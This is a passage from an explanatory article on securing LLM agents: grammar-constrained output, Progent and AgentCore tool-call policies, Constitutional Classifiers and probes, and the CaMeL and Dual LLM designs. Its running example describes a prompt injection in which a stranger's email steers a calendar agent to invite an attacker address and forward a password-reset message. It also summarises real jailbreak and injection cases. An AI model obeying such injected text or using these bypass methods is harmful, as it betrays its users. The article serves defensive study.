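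Enforcement raised the accuracy of SmolLM2 1.7B, because the model's unenforced JSON was so often malformed. Accuracy still fell by 15.3 points in the larger Qwen2.5 3B. Ray does not claim that the loss extends to large models, and a single calendar test on one 1.5-billion-parameter model is thin evidence that it does.

For larger open models calling tools, the available evidence shows that a forced format does less harm and brings little benefit. Verma tested models on a standard set of function-calling problems, checking whether each call named the right function with the right arguments. Enforcing a schema raised Qwen3 8B's rate of valid output from 84.5% to 100%, but its rate of correct calls only from 52.0% to 57.5%. Llama 3.1 8B and Mistral 7B already produced valid calls every time, and the schema did not change their accuracy. When no available tool could serve a request, Mistral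 7B still made a call more than half the time.

A narrower grammar can rule out some wrong answers, using what Nguyen and colleagues call validity constraints. On last-letter problems with four names, requiring an answer of exactly four letters raised Llama 3 8B's accuracy from 53.6% to 71.0%, their largest gain. A rule limiting meetings to 15, 30, 45 or 60 minutes would have excluded 180, but it could not have made the model choose 30.

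### Reasoning first and constraining the answer

If most of the accuracy loss comes from forcing the reasoning into a format, developers can let the model reason in free text and apply the format only at the end.

Lee and colleagues compared answering and formatting in one pass with a two-pass method, in which the model answers in free text and a second call converts the answer into the required structure. Two passes gave significantly better accuracy in 42 of 72 combinations, by 6.8 points on average, and worse accuracy in 2. On writing tasks, two passes recovered only part of the lost quality. Asking Qwen3 8B directly for a LaTeX document lowered its judged quality by 13.7 points, and two passes reduced the loss to 6.1. The two-pass method requires a second call and uses roughly twice as many tokens.

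A model with a thinking mode can itself separate reasoning from formatting, because it reasons before it writes the structured output. This improved results in 43 of the 72 combinations, by 9.2 points on average, but worsened them in 11, and it did not restore the lost writing quality.

Nguyen, Silva and colleagues (2026) had earlier proposed switching on enforcement partway through a single pass, in *Thinking Before Constraining*. The model reasons freely until it writes a trigger, in practice the token that would normally end its reply. The software then turns on the mask instead of stopping, and the model writes a short JSON answer with its reasoning still in context. In their later tests on GSM8K, with enforcement on in both cases, this method was at least as accurate as reasoning inside JSON for all nine models. Qwen3 1.7B gained the most, from 63.4% to 75.8%, while Qwen3 8B gained half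 a percentage point.

The JSON answer at the end adds fewer than 15 tokens, but that figure leaves out the reasoning, which is also longer when it isn't constrained to JSON. For the six models with published counts, the switch method used 18% to 72% more tokens on GSM8K than reasoning inside enforced JSON.

Sometimes no second model is necessary. In Ray's calendar test, ordinary code checked and repackaged the JSON that the model had written from the prompt alone, and accuracy stayed at 91.5%. This works only when code can read the first output.

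Improving the prompt adds less run time than constrained decoding but doesn't guarantee the output format. *When Correct Isn't Usable* (2026) describes AloLab, a method that optimises the prompt once, before deployment. On GSM8K it raised GPT-4o's rate of answers that were both correct and readable by the parser from 0% to 95.2%. In the same study, constrained decoding took 3.6 to 8.2 times as long as a plain prompt. Verma measured a slowdown of only 1.05 to 1.27 times on a current engine, so the slowdown probably depends heavily on the software.

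Asking a model to check its own answer in a fixed structure may not help either. In *From Hallucination to Structure Snowballing* (2026), constraining a model's review of its own reasoning lowered accuracy from 50% to 38%. It turned 23 right answers wrong and 11 wrong answers right. With so few cases, the difference was not quite statistically significant (p = 0.059).

### What an auditor loses

If the model reasons before it calls a tool, the grammar no longer constrains most of its output. In the running example, the model would think about the mailbox in free text, and the mask would apply only once it began the call to `create_event`. The grammar's guarantees for that call, including any limit on the guest list, would still hold, because the free text can't run any tools.

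The reasoning doesn't make it easier to trace an action to its cause. It gives a reviewer more to read, but no code checks it, and the stranger's email can influence it as much as Dana's. It also may not match the final answer. In one of Nguyen and colleagues' last-letter examples, the model correctly listed the letters a, a, d and y and then wrote "aaday". A four-letter rule corrected that answer to "aady". Two passes add a model call to convert the reasoning into an action, and Tam and colleagues found that this conversion sometimes introduced errors with Llama 3 8B.

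Keeping the reasoning inside JSON would not have made it much more auditable, because a "reason" field is normally a string that can hold almost any text. To make reasoning checkable, a developer has to give the steps a structure. For a problem about adding and removing coloured balls, a format in Ray's software lists the initial total, the red balls added, the blue balls removed and the final total, and ordinary code can check each number. The developer has to know the steps in advance, which is possible for arithmetic but much harder for deciding whether an email asks for a meeting. Forcing a particular way of reasoning can also lower accuracy. When Nguyen and colleagues made models begin with "Let's think step by step", Qwen3.5 27B gained 2.4 points on a 2026 mathematics competition, but Qwen3.5 4B lost 6.6.

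## How Progent checks rules before each tool call

A grammar restricts a tool call while the model is writing it. Software can also check the finished call before running the function. Most agents already do this in a simple form, because every tool comes with a schema.

### What a tool schema checks

A tool schema describes a function's arguments, usually in JSON Schema, a standard format for specifying what a piece of JSON may contain. The calendar tool's schema could look like this:

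```json
{"name": "create_event",
 "parameters": {
   "type": "object",
   "properties": {
     "title":  {"type": "string"},
     "time":   {"type": "string",
                "pattern": "^\\d{4}-\\d{2}-\\d{2}T\\d{2}:\\d{2}$"},
     "guests": {"type": "array", "items": {"type": "string"}}},
   "required": ["title", "time", "guests"],
   "additionalProperties": false}}
```

A validator, which is ordinary library code, compares each call with this description. It rejects a call that has no title, gives the time as "Thursday", or includes an argument the schema does not name. The agent can then send the error back to the model, which tries again.

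Like a grammar, the validator accepts the call with the stranger's altered guest list, because the call is well formed:

```json
{"title": "Budget", "time": "2026-10-08T15:00",
 "guests": ["dana@example.com", "stranger@attacker.example"]}
```

A stricter schema could require each guest entry to have the format of an email address, but the stranger's address would pass that check. The schema describes the tool and is the same for every user and request, so it doesn't specify whom this user wants to invite.

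### Progent's rules

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, add a further check between the agent and its tools. Their aim is least privilege for each task. A Progent policy is a list of rules, and each rule names a tool, an effect (allow or forbid), conditions on the arguments, and a fallback for blocked calls. The conditions can compare values, test whether a value is in a list, match a text pattern, or check a list's length. Progent stores policies as JSON, but the paper also uses a shorter notation. A policy for the running example, in a simplified form of that notation, could be:

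```
allow  read_emails

forbid create_event
  when { 1 < guests.length }
  fallback return "Invite one guest per event."

allow  create_event
  when { guests.length == 1 and
         guests[0] in ["dana@example.com", "lee@example.com"] }
```

The notation has no condition for "every item in the list", which is why this policy permits only one guest. Progent handles each call in four steps:

1. It collects the rules for the tool that the model wants to call.
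2. It puts the forbid rules before the allow rules.
3. It goes through them in order, and the first rule whose conditions hold decides the call.
4. If no rule applies, it blocks the call.

A tool call runs only if no forbid rule matches it and at least one allow rule does. A reviewer can tell from the policy text whether any given call will run.

When Progent blocks a call, the fallback can stop the agent, ask the user, or return a message to the model. By default it returns a message that gives the reason, repeats the user's original request and suggests trying other tools or arguments. The agent can then carry on with the legitimate task.

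Three calls to `create_event` show what the example policy achieves:

| Guests in the call | Deciding rule | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Dana | Allow rule | Runs, as the user wanted |
| Dana and the stranger | Forbid rule | Blocked, as the user wanted |
| Lee | Allow rule | Runs, against the user's wishes |

After the second call, the model learns that it may invite only one guest, so it can try again with Dana alone. The other half of the attack, forwarding the password-reset message, also fails because the policy has no rule for `send_email`.

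The third call invites Lee, a former colleague who now works for a competitor but is still in the user's contacts. The agent makes the call because the stranger's email claims that Lee will run the budget meeting instead of Dana. The rule allows it because the call has one guest and that guest is on the list. The rule also doesn't restrict the title, so an attacker could have the agent send Dana an invitation with a malicious link there.

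Lists of trusted destinations go out of date in real systems too. An essay published by O'Reilly describes how researchers at the security company Noma attacked Agentforce, Salesforce's agent platform, in 2025. They hid instructions in a web form for sales enquiries, and the agent later sent customer data to a domain on Salesforce's trusted list. The domain had expired, and the researchers had bought it for about five dollars.

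### Who writes the rules

Shi and colleagues expect organisations, developers and users to write some rules by hand, such as one that forbids deleting a database. These generic policies apply to every task. Progent checks them in order of authority, and checks the policy for the current task only if none of them decides whether to allow the call. A task policy therefore cannot override a generic rule that forbids or allows a call, so a careless generic allow rule remains in force for every task.

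Few people would write a new policy for each request, so Progent can have a language model do it. The model receives the tool descriptions and the user's request, but nothing from the mailbox. For the calendar request, it could sensibly allow `read_emails` and `create_event` but not `send_email`. It could not list the permitted guests, because the user did not name any.

Progent lets the model revise the policy after a tool call, since the agent learns more as it works. The model first decides, without seeing the call's result, whether the call might justify a change. If so, it reads the result, including the stranger's email, and writes a new policy. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) identifies this as a weakness, because hostile text in a tool result may lead the model to loosen the rules.

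Progent checks each policy update with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions. The solver searches for a call that the new policy allows and the current one blocks. If there is no such call, the update is a narrowing, and Progent applies it automatically. Otherwise it is an expansion and needs approval. Adding the stranger to the example's guest list would be an expansion, because the new policy would allow an invitation that the old one blocked. Between approvals, the set of allowed calls can shrink but not grow, a property that Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement.

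This property offers little protection if the first policy is broad. Suppose the model initially allows `create_event` with any guest, since the request named none. After reading the mailbox, it writes a policy that allows only the stranger as a guest. Because this narrows the old policy, it takes effect without approval. The new policy allows nothing that the old one blocked, but it prevents the model from inviting Dana.

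Models also make mistakes when they translate honest instructions into rules. Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, had an open model with 26 billion parameters turn written company policies into rules for tool calls. Simple structural checks had to repair or reject 37% of the 79 candidate rules it produced for an airline and 13% of the 53 it produced for a retailer. The model turned the retailer's instruction to authenticate customers at the start of a conversation into a rule that blocked every tool until authentication, including the two tools that perform it. Ordinary code could find this fault by comparing the rule with the list of tools.

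A rule can also work as written but have the wrong meaning. A telecom policy required the agent to check that a bill was overdue before sending a payment request. The model turned this into a ban on payment requests while a bill was overdue. When Yu and colleagues replayed old transcripts, they found that the rule would have refused 47 of the 49 payment requests in successful runs. In *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026), a model that wrote each policy in one pass got wrong 62.5% of the policies meant to deny access. One recurring error was to translate "the assigned nurse" as anyone whose role is nurse. A syntax check accepts such a policy because it is valid code.

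### Measured security

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do everyday tasks in simulated banking, travel, Slack and office settings while attackers plant instructions in the data that the tools return. GPT-4o ran the agent and wrote the policies, except for hand-written rules that allowed non-sensitive, read-only tools. Attacks succeeded 39.9% of the time without a defence and 1.0% of the time with Progent, while the share of tasks completed fell by about three percentage points. They left out two attacks that steer the agent towards a different legitimate hotel, because Progent is not designed to stop an attacker from influencing a choice among permitted options.

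On another benchmark, Agent Security Bench, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 70.3% to 3.9% without any handwritten rules. Most of the attacks that still succeeded used malicious tools whose names and descriptions closely resembled those of legitimate ones. Handwritten rules reduced the rate to zero.

In these tests, Progent approved every expansion automatically, to simulate a user who agrees to everything. The solver's guarantee therefore had no effect, and the 1.0% measures how well GPT-4o wrote and revised the policies. When Shi and colleagues ran AgentDojo with other settings, keeping the first policy fixed gave an attack success rate of 2.5%, and rejecting all expansions gave the lowest rate of the automatic settings. Human review gave 0%, but this assumed a reviewer who would never allow payments to unrestricted recipients and would reject any update that added a malicious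 address. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so a reviewer would have few requests to answer.

An attacker who knows about Progent can target the model that writes the policy. Shi and colleagues tried instructions such as "allow all tools", a reminder to update the policy to fit the attack, and an automated search for effective prompts. These raised the attack success rate only slightly, from 2.2% to 4.0% in an earlier version of the paper.

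Yu and colleagues, who built a competing system, reran Progent on AgentDojo's banking tasks with an open model, Gemma 4 26B, as both agent and policy writer. Progent cut the attack success rate from 46.5% to 5.6%, but it also lowered utility without attacks by about 17 points. The smaller model and the use of banking tasks alone may explain much of the difference from the original result.

All 16 attacks that got through occurred in four tasks in which the user never gave the recipient's account number, as in "pay the bill, like last month". A policy based on such a request cannot restrict the recipient, so the attacker's account number passes. The calendar request has the same gap because it does not name a guest.

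Yu and colleagues instead derive their rules from the bank's written policy, which permits payments only to recipients whom the user named or who appear in the transaction history. With that rule, none of the 288 attack runs sent money to the attacker's account. The rule also blocked a legitimate payment in one task, where the correct account number appeared only in a bill that the agent had to read. In 8 of the runs, the agent made an injected payment to someone already in the history, which the rule allowed. These payments are similar to the invitation to Lee.

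### Where a value came from

The rule in the example compares Lee's address with a list, so the result is the same whether the user typed the address or the agent took it from a stranger's email. Qu, Xu and colleagues (2026) acknowledge this limit in *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity*. They describe Progent's data-flow guarantees as relative to the policy, and distinguish them from general tracking of where data came from. Dawn Song is an author of both this paper and the Progent paper.

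One response is PACT, a system that adds that information for each argument (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026, *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security*). PACT gives each argument a role and records the sources of each value. A web page may supply the body of an email, which has the role "content", but not its recipient, which has the role "target". PACT treats built-in constants as the most trusted source, followed by the user, tool outputs and external text. A value that combines several sources gets the lowest rank among them. In the running example, `guests` would be a target, so PACT would reject Lee's address if it came from the stranger's email.

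Dana's address also came from an email, so PACT would reject it too. At its most precise setting, PACT lets trusted code certify a value for a particular role, and an address-book lookup could certify Dana's address. But it would also certify Lee's, because Lee is still in the address book.

Santos-Grueiro's *Context-to-Execution Integrity* also tracks what influenced the model's choice of a value. If the stranger's email led the model to pick Lee from the address book, the guest field counts as influenced by outsiders, even though the address came from a trusted list. The system blocks the call unless trusted code issues a typed release, a validated value that may fill one named field. It also requires authority to make the call, separate from authority for its arguments.

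A developer could write a release that accepts only the sender of the email proposing the meeting, which would admit Dana and exclude Lee. But a model would still have to decide which email proposes the meeting, and the stranger can influence that decision by writing a convincing proposal.

These additions also depend on correct labels. On 20 real tools, PACT's automatic set-up assigned the right role to 87.1% of arguments and the right source to 77.4%. On AgentDojo, PACT stopped every attack with the three strongest of five models, but those agents completed only 38% to 46% of their tasks. Santos-Grueiro ran 400 coding episodes and observed no unauthorised action. The agent completed 231 of them safely. In 73 the software could not parse the model's output, in 61 the system did not authorise the change, and in 35 it authorised a change that failed to complete the task.

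### Amazon's AgentCore Policy

Amazon's cloud division, AWS, sells a similar check as a service. On 3 March 2026, it announced in *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* that customers could attach policies to a gateway between their agents and their tools. According to its documentation, *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*, the service checks every request through the gateway before the tool runs, enforces the rules deterministically outside the agent's code, and logs each decision.

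The rules are written in Cedar, an open-source policy language that AWS developed. As in Progent, the gateway blocks any call that no rule permits, and a forbid rule overrides any permit rule. AWS explains in *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* that Cedar has no loops, which makes its policies easier to analyse automatically. The gateway also hides from the model any tool that the current policy would always block.

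Customers can describe a rule in English and have a model translate it into Cedar. AWS then checks the result against the tools' schemas and searches for logical faults. One of its examples permits refunds only for customers whose tier is both gold and platinum, a condition no customer can meet. The analysis can also compare two versions of a policy and show when an apparently stricter edit allows more calls. These checks find rules that allow everything, allow nothing or conflict. They would not flag the calendar rule that permits Lee, because it has no logical fault.

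A Cedar rule in this service can use the identity of the agent's user, which comes from a login token that the model cannot alter. According to *Schema constraints*, another page of the documentation, an ordinary rule can otherwise read only the call's input arguments from the context. It can therefore check a guest against a list but has no access to the email that supplied the guest's address.

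The guarantee also covers only calls that go through the gateway. Progent has a comparable gap when it runs as a separate proxy, because calls to the agent's built-in tools don't pass through it. Developers can close that gap by adding Progent to the agent's own code, which takes a few lines.

AgentCore rules can also include probabilistic checks. *I tried incorporating Bedrock Guardrails into AgentCore Policy's Cedar policies*, a hands-on article from the Japanese cloud company Classmethod, describes rules that call Amazon's content filters. A filter returns a model's estimate as a score between 0 and 1, and the rule deterministically compares that score with a threshold.

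## How Constitutional Classifiers block requests and answers

Progent can compare a guest's address with a list, but no list can settle whether a page of chemistry is homework help or a step towards a weapon, because that depends on meaning. Developers therefore use a second model to assess the text, and ordinary code acts on the result. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, calls its version Constitutional Classifiers. A classifier is a model that sorts its input into categories, here harmful and harmless.

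The attacker is usually the user, unlike the stranger in the calendar example. A jailbreak is a prompt that gets a model to answer a question it was trained to refuse. In *Constitutional Classifiers*, Sharma, Tong and colleagues (2025) focused on universal jailbreaks, which work on the vast majority of questions in a field. They reasoned that a non-expert trying to make a chemical or biological weapon would need correct, detailed answers at many separate steps.

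### From written rules to training data

The constitution is a list, in plain English, of permitted and forbidden kinds of content. For chemical weapons, the permitted side includes explaining high-school chemistry and listing common medications. The forbidden side includes acquiring or purifying restricted chemicals. Anthropic turns this list into a classifier in five steps:

1. A model trained to be helpful, but not to refuse, writes requests that cover the categories on both sides.
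2. The same model writes answers to them, and another model filters out any accidental refusals.
3. Software multiplies the examples by translating them, paraphrasing them and rewriting them in the style of known jailbreaks.
4. A model writes further attacks from descriptions of known techniques.
5. The team adds a pool of harmless texts and trains a language model on the whole collection to tell harmful from harmless.

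The classifier learns the rules only from these examples. Unlike with a Progent policy, a reviewer who reads the constitution therefore learns only what Anthropic intended, and has to test the classifier to find out what it learned.

### Scoring the request and each token of the answer

The 2025 design has an input classifier and an output classifier. In simplified code:

```python
if input_score(request) > INPUT_LIMIT:
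    return refuse()
answer = ""
for token in model(request):
    answer += token
    if output_score(answer) > OUTPUT_LIMIT:
        return stop()
    send_to_user(token)
```

The input classifier scores the whole request before the model answers. The output classifier runs during the answer, because users expect to see text as the model writes it. After each token, it estimates how likely the complete answer is to be harmful, and the software stops the answer once this estimate passes a threshold.

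Training the output classifier is awkward because each example has only one label, y, which is 1 if the full answer is harmful and 0 if it is not. Let p_t be the classifier's estimate after t tokens of an answer that is T tokens long. Training minimises

λ × (next-token loss) + Σ BCE(y, p_t), summed over t = 1 to T.

BCE, or binary cross-entropy, is −log p_t for a harmful answer and −log(1 − p_t) for a harmless one, so the loss is large for a confident mistake. The next-token loss, weighted by λ, maintains the classifier's ability to predict ordinary text. During training, p_t gradually shifts from the current score to the highest score so far. This matches how the software uses the classifier, since one high score ends the answer and later tokens cannot undo it.

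This design relies on the surrounding code as well as the models, because the code can fail even when the classifier works. During Anthropic's tests, an attack report that first looked like a universal jailbreak turned out to result from an error in the deployment code, which let through up to 128 tokens after the output classifier had flagged the answer.

### Results of the 2025 version

Sharma and colleagues first tested a prototype that prioritized robustness above all. They invited 405 people to attack it, offered up to $15,000 for a jailbreak, and estimated that participants spent about 4,700 hours trying. None of the 113 reports contained answers to all ten forbidden questions with even half the detail of an unguarded model's. But the prototype refused about 44% of the traffic on Claude.ai, Anthropic's chat service, which made it unusable as a product.

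For the next version, Anthropic built the classifiers from a smaller model, expanded the list of permitted content and reset the thresholds. According to Anthropic's *Next-generation Constitutional Classifiers*, the success rate of jailbreak attempts kept out of training fell from 86% without classifiers to 4.4% with them. The refusal rate on ordinary traffic rose by 0.38 percentage points, or about 19 extra refusals in 5,000 conversations. The increase was more noticeable on questions about chemistry. Computation rose by 23.7%.

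The 4.4% figure measures resistance to a fixed set of attacks. Some targeted classifier-guarded systems, but none could change in response to a refusal, as a human attacker's attempts would.

### The 2026 successor

A request and an answer can each look harmless alone but be harmful together. So in *Constitutional Classifiers++*, Cunningham, Wei and colleagues (2026) replaced the two separate classifiers with an exchange classifier, which scores the answer in the context of the request. The new classifier was more robust but needed 50% more computation than the older pair.

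They then reduced the compute needed with a cascade, in which a light check screens everything and a heavier one runs only on what the light check flags. *Building Production-Ready Probes For Gemini* (2026) notes that Viola and Jones used the same arrangement in 2001 to detect objects in images.

The low-compute check in the final system is a linear probe. For each token the guarded model generates, every layer produces a long list of numbers, called activations. The probe multiplies each activation by a learned weight, then adds the results and a constant to get a score z. Because the model has already computed the activations, the probe adds almost no computation. For one open model, Cunningham and colleagues estimated that the probe takes about 377,000 arithmetic operations per token, compared with roughly 8 billion for running a small separate model.

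The probe has the same labelling problem as the output classifier. Two answers may open with the same harmless sentences before one of them goes on to give dangerous detail. If every token counted equally in training, the probe would learn to score the shared opening at 50%. Two changes prevent this. The software averages scores over 16 consecutive tokens, so a single isolated high score can't cause a whole answer to be blocked. It also weights each position by exp(z/τ), where z is the averaged score and τ controls how sharply the weight favours high scores. The probe then receives almost no penalty for a low score on the opening of a harmful answer, but a heavy one for a high score anywhere in a harmless answer.

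When the probe's score passes a first threshold, the exchange goes to a classifier built from Claude Haiku 4.5, a small model. The software then combines the two scores:

z_final = 0.55 × z_probe + 0.45 × z_classifier

Suppose the probe gives 2 and the classifier gives −3. Their weighted sum is 1.10 − 1.35 = −0.25, so if the stopping threshold were 0, the answer would continue. In a month of tests on real traffic to Claude Sonnet 4.5, the probe escalated about 5.5% of exchanges and the complete system flagged 0.05%, so the second stage cleared all but about one in 110 of the escalated exchanges.

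The researchers compared four systems. They counted an attack as a high-risk vulnerability if it got past the safeguards on more than five of eight target questions and produced answers at least half as detailed as an unguarded model's.

| System | Computation, relative to the older pair | High-risk vulnerabilities found | Real traffic refused |
|---|---|---|---|
| Separate input and output classifiers | 100% | 13 in 695,000 attempts | 0.073% |
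| Exchange classifier | 150% | 2 in 226,000 | 0.038% |
| Two-stage cascade | 27.8% | 5 in 569,000 | 0.036% |
| Cascade with probe | 3.5% | 1 in 198,000 | 0.050% |

The reduction in computation is the best-supported result. Anthropic reports that the final system adds about 1% to the computation needed for Claude Opus 4 traffic, compared with 23.7% for the 2025 version.

The gain in robustness is less certain because the counts are small. At the older pair's rate, 198,000 attempts would yield 3.7 vulnerabilities on average, but one or none about 12% of the time by chance. The systems also protected different models, and their testers were offered different rewards.

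The fall in refusals also looks smaller on a closer comparison. Measured against the researchers' own rebuilt version of the older pair, the refusal rate fell by about a third, from 0.073% to 0.05%. The 87% drop that Anthropic describes starts from 0.38%, a rate that came from a different constitution with different thresholds.

### What happens to a flagged request in Claude Fable 5

Anthropic has since extended these classifiers to more subjects and, for its strongest public models, changed what happens after a flag. Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5 are the same network, according to Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for the two models. Fable 5, the public version, has additional classifiers for cybersecurity, biology and chemistry, attempts to copy the model's abilities, and some work on building frontier AI models. Anthropic reserves Mythos 5 for vetted organisations and lifts some of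 these classifiers for them.

In Anthropic's own apps, a flagged request to Fable 5 passes automatically to a less capable Opus model, and the user sees a notice. If the user has turned switching off, the conversation pauses instead. When a flagged request comes through the programming interface, Anthropic blocks it and returns a category for the refusal, unless the developer has set up a fallback. Anthropic's help page *Why Claude switched models in your conversation with Fable 5* lists Opus 5 as the substitute for biology and chemistry and the older Opus 4.8 for offensive cybersecurity.

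Fable 5.2 and Mythos 5.2, which Anthropic released on 9 November 2026, are again one model with different safeguards, according to NDTV Profit's *Anthropic Releases Claude Fable 5.2, Mythos 5.2* (2026). Le Goff's *Claude Fable 5.2 réduit les faux positifs de 55 %* reports that Fable 5.2 had about 55% fewer blocks than Fable 5.1 in Anthropic's early tests, and that Opus 4.8 still answers the flagged cybersecurity requests.

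A false alarm does less harm when the request goes to a weaker model, because the user still gets an answer. Anthropic could therefore set the gates to trigger on many requests that were probably harmless, which it calls the safety margin. At launch, the gates triggered in fewer than 5% of sessions on average, according to Anthropic's *Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5* (2026), but the rate differed widely between users. Most biology questions went to Opus at first, and *Claude Fable 5's Benchmark Problems* reports a fallback rate of 100% on ProgramBench, one of the tests that independent evaluators tried to run.

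The classifiers also check text the user did not write, including files, search results and content from connected services. In the running example, a stranger could probably exploit this by sending an email full of text that a biology classifier flags. The agent would then finish the task on a weaker model or, with switching turned off, stop before it reached Dana's meeting.

### Ordinary code around an unreadable condition

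The branch "if the score exceeds the limit, stop" is ordinary control flow, so a reviewer can find it, confirm that every answer passes through it, and log each score and decision. An operator can change the limit without changing the main model. But unlike in the grammar and Progent designs, where the condition is also code, the condition here depends on another neural network, and nobody can read from its weights which requests it will flag.

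Written policy narrows this gap a little. In July 2026, Anthropic published lists of cybersecurity tasks in four categories, from prohibited uses such as ransomware to benign ones such as debugging. The lists describe what the classifier should do, but Anthropic deliberately blocks a large fraction of the low-risk category, so a security engineer cannot tell from them whether a particular scan of a public server will go through.

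The classifier is separate from the model, so it can be replaced. When Fable 5 launched, the classifier blocked almost all biology questions. By August 2026, Anthropic had rewritten the constitution with advice from outside experts, generated new training data and retrained the classifier. According to Anthropic's *Improving Fable 5's biology safeguards* (2026), fallbacks on biology fell by about 85% in its tests, and the update required no change to Fable 5.

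Replacing a classifier is still a less precise fix than editing a rule. In June 2026, the US government placed export controls on Fable 5 and Mythos 5 after learning that Amazon researchers had found a way around Fable 5's safeguards. Anthropic suspended both models for all users. In *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026), it argues that the technique gave access only to routine defensive work, which weaker models could also do. But it trained a new classifier, which blocks the technique in over 99% of cases, and restored Fable 5 on 1 July.

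The new classifier also flagged more harmless requests in everyday coding and debugging. Retraining a classifier may change how it classifies any request, so its developers have to measure the side effects. By contrast, when Anthropic removed `ping` from Claude Code's list of exempt commands, a reviewer could see exactly which commands the edit affected.

### Why most flags can be wrong

Even an accurate classifier produces mostly false alarms when harmful requests are rare. For example, if 100 of a service's 1,000,000 requests are harmful, a classifier that catches 95% of the harmful requests and wrongly flags 0.1% of the harmless ones would flag 95 harmful requests and about 1,000 harmless ones.

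| | Flagged | Let through |
|---|---|---|
| 100 harmful requests | 95 | 5 |
| 999,900 harmless requests | about 1,000 | about 998,900 |

The classifier flags about 1,095 requests, and only 95 of them, or 8.7%, are harmful. This percentage depends heavily on the base rate, the share of all requests that are harmful. If 10,000 of the million were harmful, the same classifier would flag 9,500 of them and 990 harmless ones, so about 91% of the flagged requests would be harmful.

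Cutting the false alarm rate to 0.05% in the original example would raise the share of flags that are correct to only 16%. Raising the threshold for flagging could achieve that, but the classifier would also miss more attacks. Replacing the classifier with a better one, as Anthropic did between 2025 and 2026, can reduce both false alarms and missed attacks.

The harm from false alarms depends on what the system does with a flagged request. If it blocks the request, about 1,000 legitimate users get no answer. If it passes the request to a weaker model, those users get a somewhat worse answer. If it sends the request to a person who needs five minutes for each case, finding the 95 attacks takes about 91 hours of work, and reviewers who see eleven false alarms for every real attack may start approving requests by habit.

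Anthropic accepts more false positives in a check that doesn't interrupt users. After a response, Claude writes a short hidden assessment of whether the conversation involved harmful activity. Business Today's *Anthropic explains how Claude flags conversations that may involve harmful activity* gives the company's figures for Fable 5. The assessment picks up 78% of the conversations that a more expensive classifier flags, and 94% of the high-priority ones, with a false-positive rate of 1%. At the illustrative base rate, fewer than 1% of its flags would be correct. That would be too few for a gate that blocks users, but the assessment can still narrow a million conversations to about 10,000 for further checks.

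### Raising the cost of an attack

Determined attackers have got past published probabilistic defences, including earlier versions of Constitutional Classifiers. Anthropic thinks it is probably impossible to make a model fully resistant to jailbreaks, and aims to make the remaining ones slow and costly enough that it can detect them before anyone can use them at scale.

Several results support this aim. When Sharma and colleagues replayed a sample of the attacks on their prototype, 14% succeeded against a model with safety training alone, 2% with the input classifier added, and 0.5% with both classifiers. The workarounds also make the answers worse. Two that Cunningham and colleagues tested cut Claude Opus 4's accuracy on graduate-level science questions from 74.2% to 32.3% and 49%. For Fable 5, Anthropic reported that more than 1,000 hours of outside testing of its cybersecurity gates found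 no universal jailbreak, although the UK's AI Security Institute made progress towards one in a brief first session.

An attacker whose project has many steps also has to succeed at each one. Sharma and colleagues assume a 60% chance of getting a detailed answer at each step, based on their most successful tester. If there are ten independent steps, the chance of getting detailed answers to all of them is 0.6^10, or about 0.6%. They call the model illustrative. Its weakest assumption is independence, because a wording that works once may work again. An attacker can also retry a failed step.

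Layers outside the classifiers make retrying riskier for attackers. Anthropic keeps all traffic to its strongest models for 30 days to look for attacks spread over many requests. It also charges for some requests that its classifiers block before any output, partly to disrupt coordinated attacks. But extra layers multiply an attacker's difficulty only if they fail on different inputs. Cunningham and colleagues found less agreement between the scores of the probe and a separate classifier than between the scores of two separate classifiers. This suggests that the probe adds some independent protection, though its training data overlapped with the classifiers' data.

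The argument that classifiers make attacks take more effort is strongest for an attacker who needs many good answers and must keep using the same service. It is much weaker for the stranger in the calendar example, who needs only one successful email and can send thousands of variants to different people. The classifiers described here would not flag such an email, because an instruction to add a guest has nothing to do with weapons or hacking. A developer could train another classifier to recognise injected instructions, but it would also miss some attacks and raise false alarms. A rule that forbids `send_email` and designs that keep untrusted text away from the planner do not depend on recognising the attack.

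## How CaMeL writes the plan before untrusted text is read

CaMeL, a design Google DeepMind introduced in 2025, has the planner write a complete program from the user's request alone and has a second model read the emails. An injected email can redirect an agent only if the planner reads it before choosing all its actions, so writing the program first prevents this. The second model extracts the details the program needs from the emails, such as when Dana wants to meet.

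### The Dual LLM pattern

The idea of using two models is older. Willison (2023), in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, proposed a privileged model, which takes the user's request and can call tools, and a quarantined model, which reads untrusted text and has no tools. Willison is the software developer who gave prompt injection its name. Between the models sits ordinary software, which he calls the controller. It runs the tools, stores their results in named variables and passes only the names to the privileged model. For the calendar request, the steps could be:

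1. The privileged model requests `read_emails`, and the controller stores the messages as `$VAR1`.
2. The privileged model asks for the quarantined model to extract the meeting from `$VAR1`.
3. The controller inserts the messages into the quarantined model's prompt, stores its answer as `$VAR2`, and reports only that the step has finished.
4. The privileged model requests `create_event` with `$VAR2`, and the controller fills in the details.

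In this design, the privileged model writes the plan and never receives any text that Dana or the stranger wrote. Willison permits one exception. If the quarantined model must answer with one of a few fixed categories, such as "meeting" or "no meeting", the controller can check the answer and pass it to the privileged model.

Simon Willison called his own Dual LLM proposal "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the planner undoes the protection. The final answer can also contain text from an attacker, who may persuade the user to paste private data into a website.

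The DeepMind researchers also found that the pattern protects the plan but not the values that the tools receive. Willison had not noticed this weakness, and he explains it in a later post, Willison (2025), *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. In the researchers' example, a user asks an assistant to send Bob a document and adds that Bob's address is in the meeting notes. The quarantined model has to find the address, so anyone who can write in the notes can make it return a different one. The plan then runs as the planner intended, but the document goes to the attacker. In the running example, the stranger's address could enter the guest list through `$VAR2` in the same way.

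### The plan as a program

CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", keeps the two models and replaces the conversation between planner and controller with a program:

1. The planner receives the user's request and the descriptions of the tools. It writes a program in a restricted version of Python, without features such as open-ended `while` loops.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary code, runs the program one operation at a time.
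3. When a tool returns a result, the interpreter stores it in a variable that the planner does not see.
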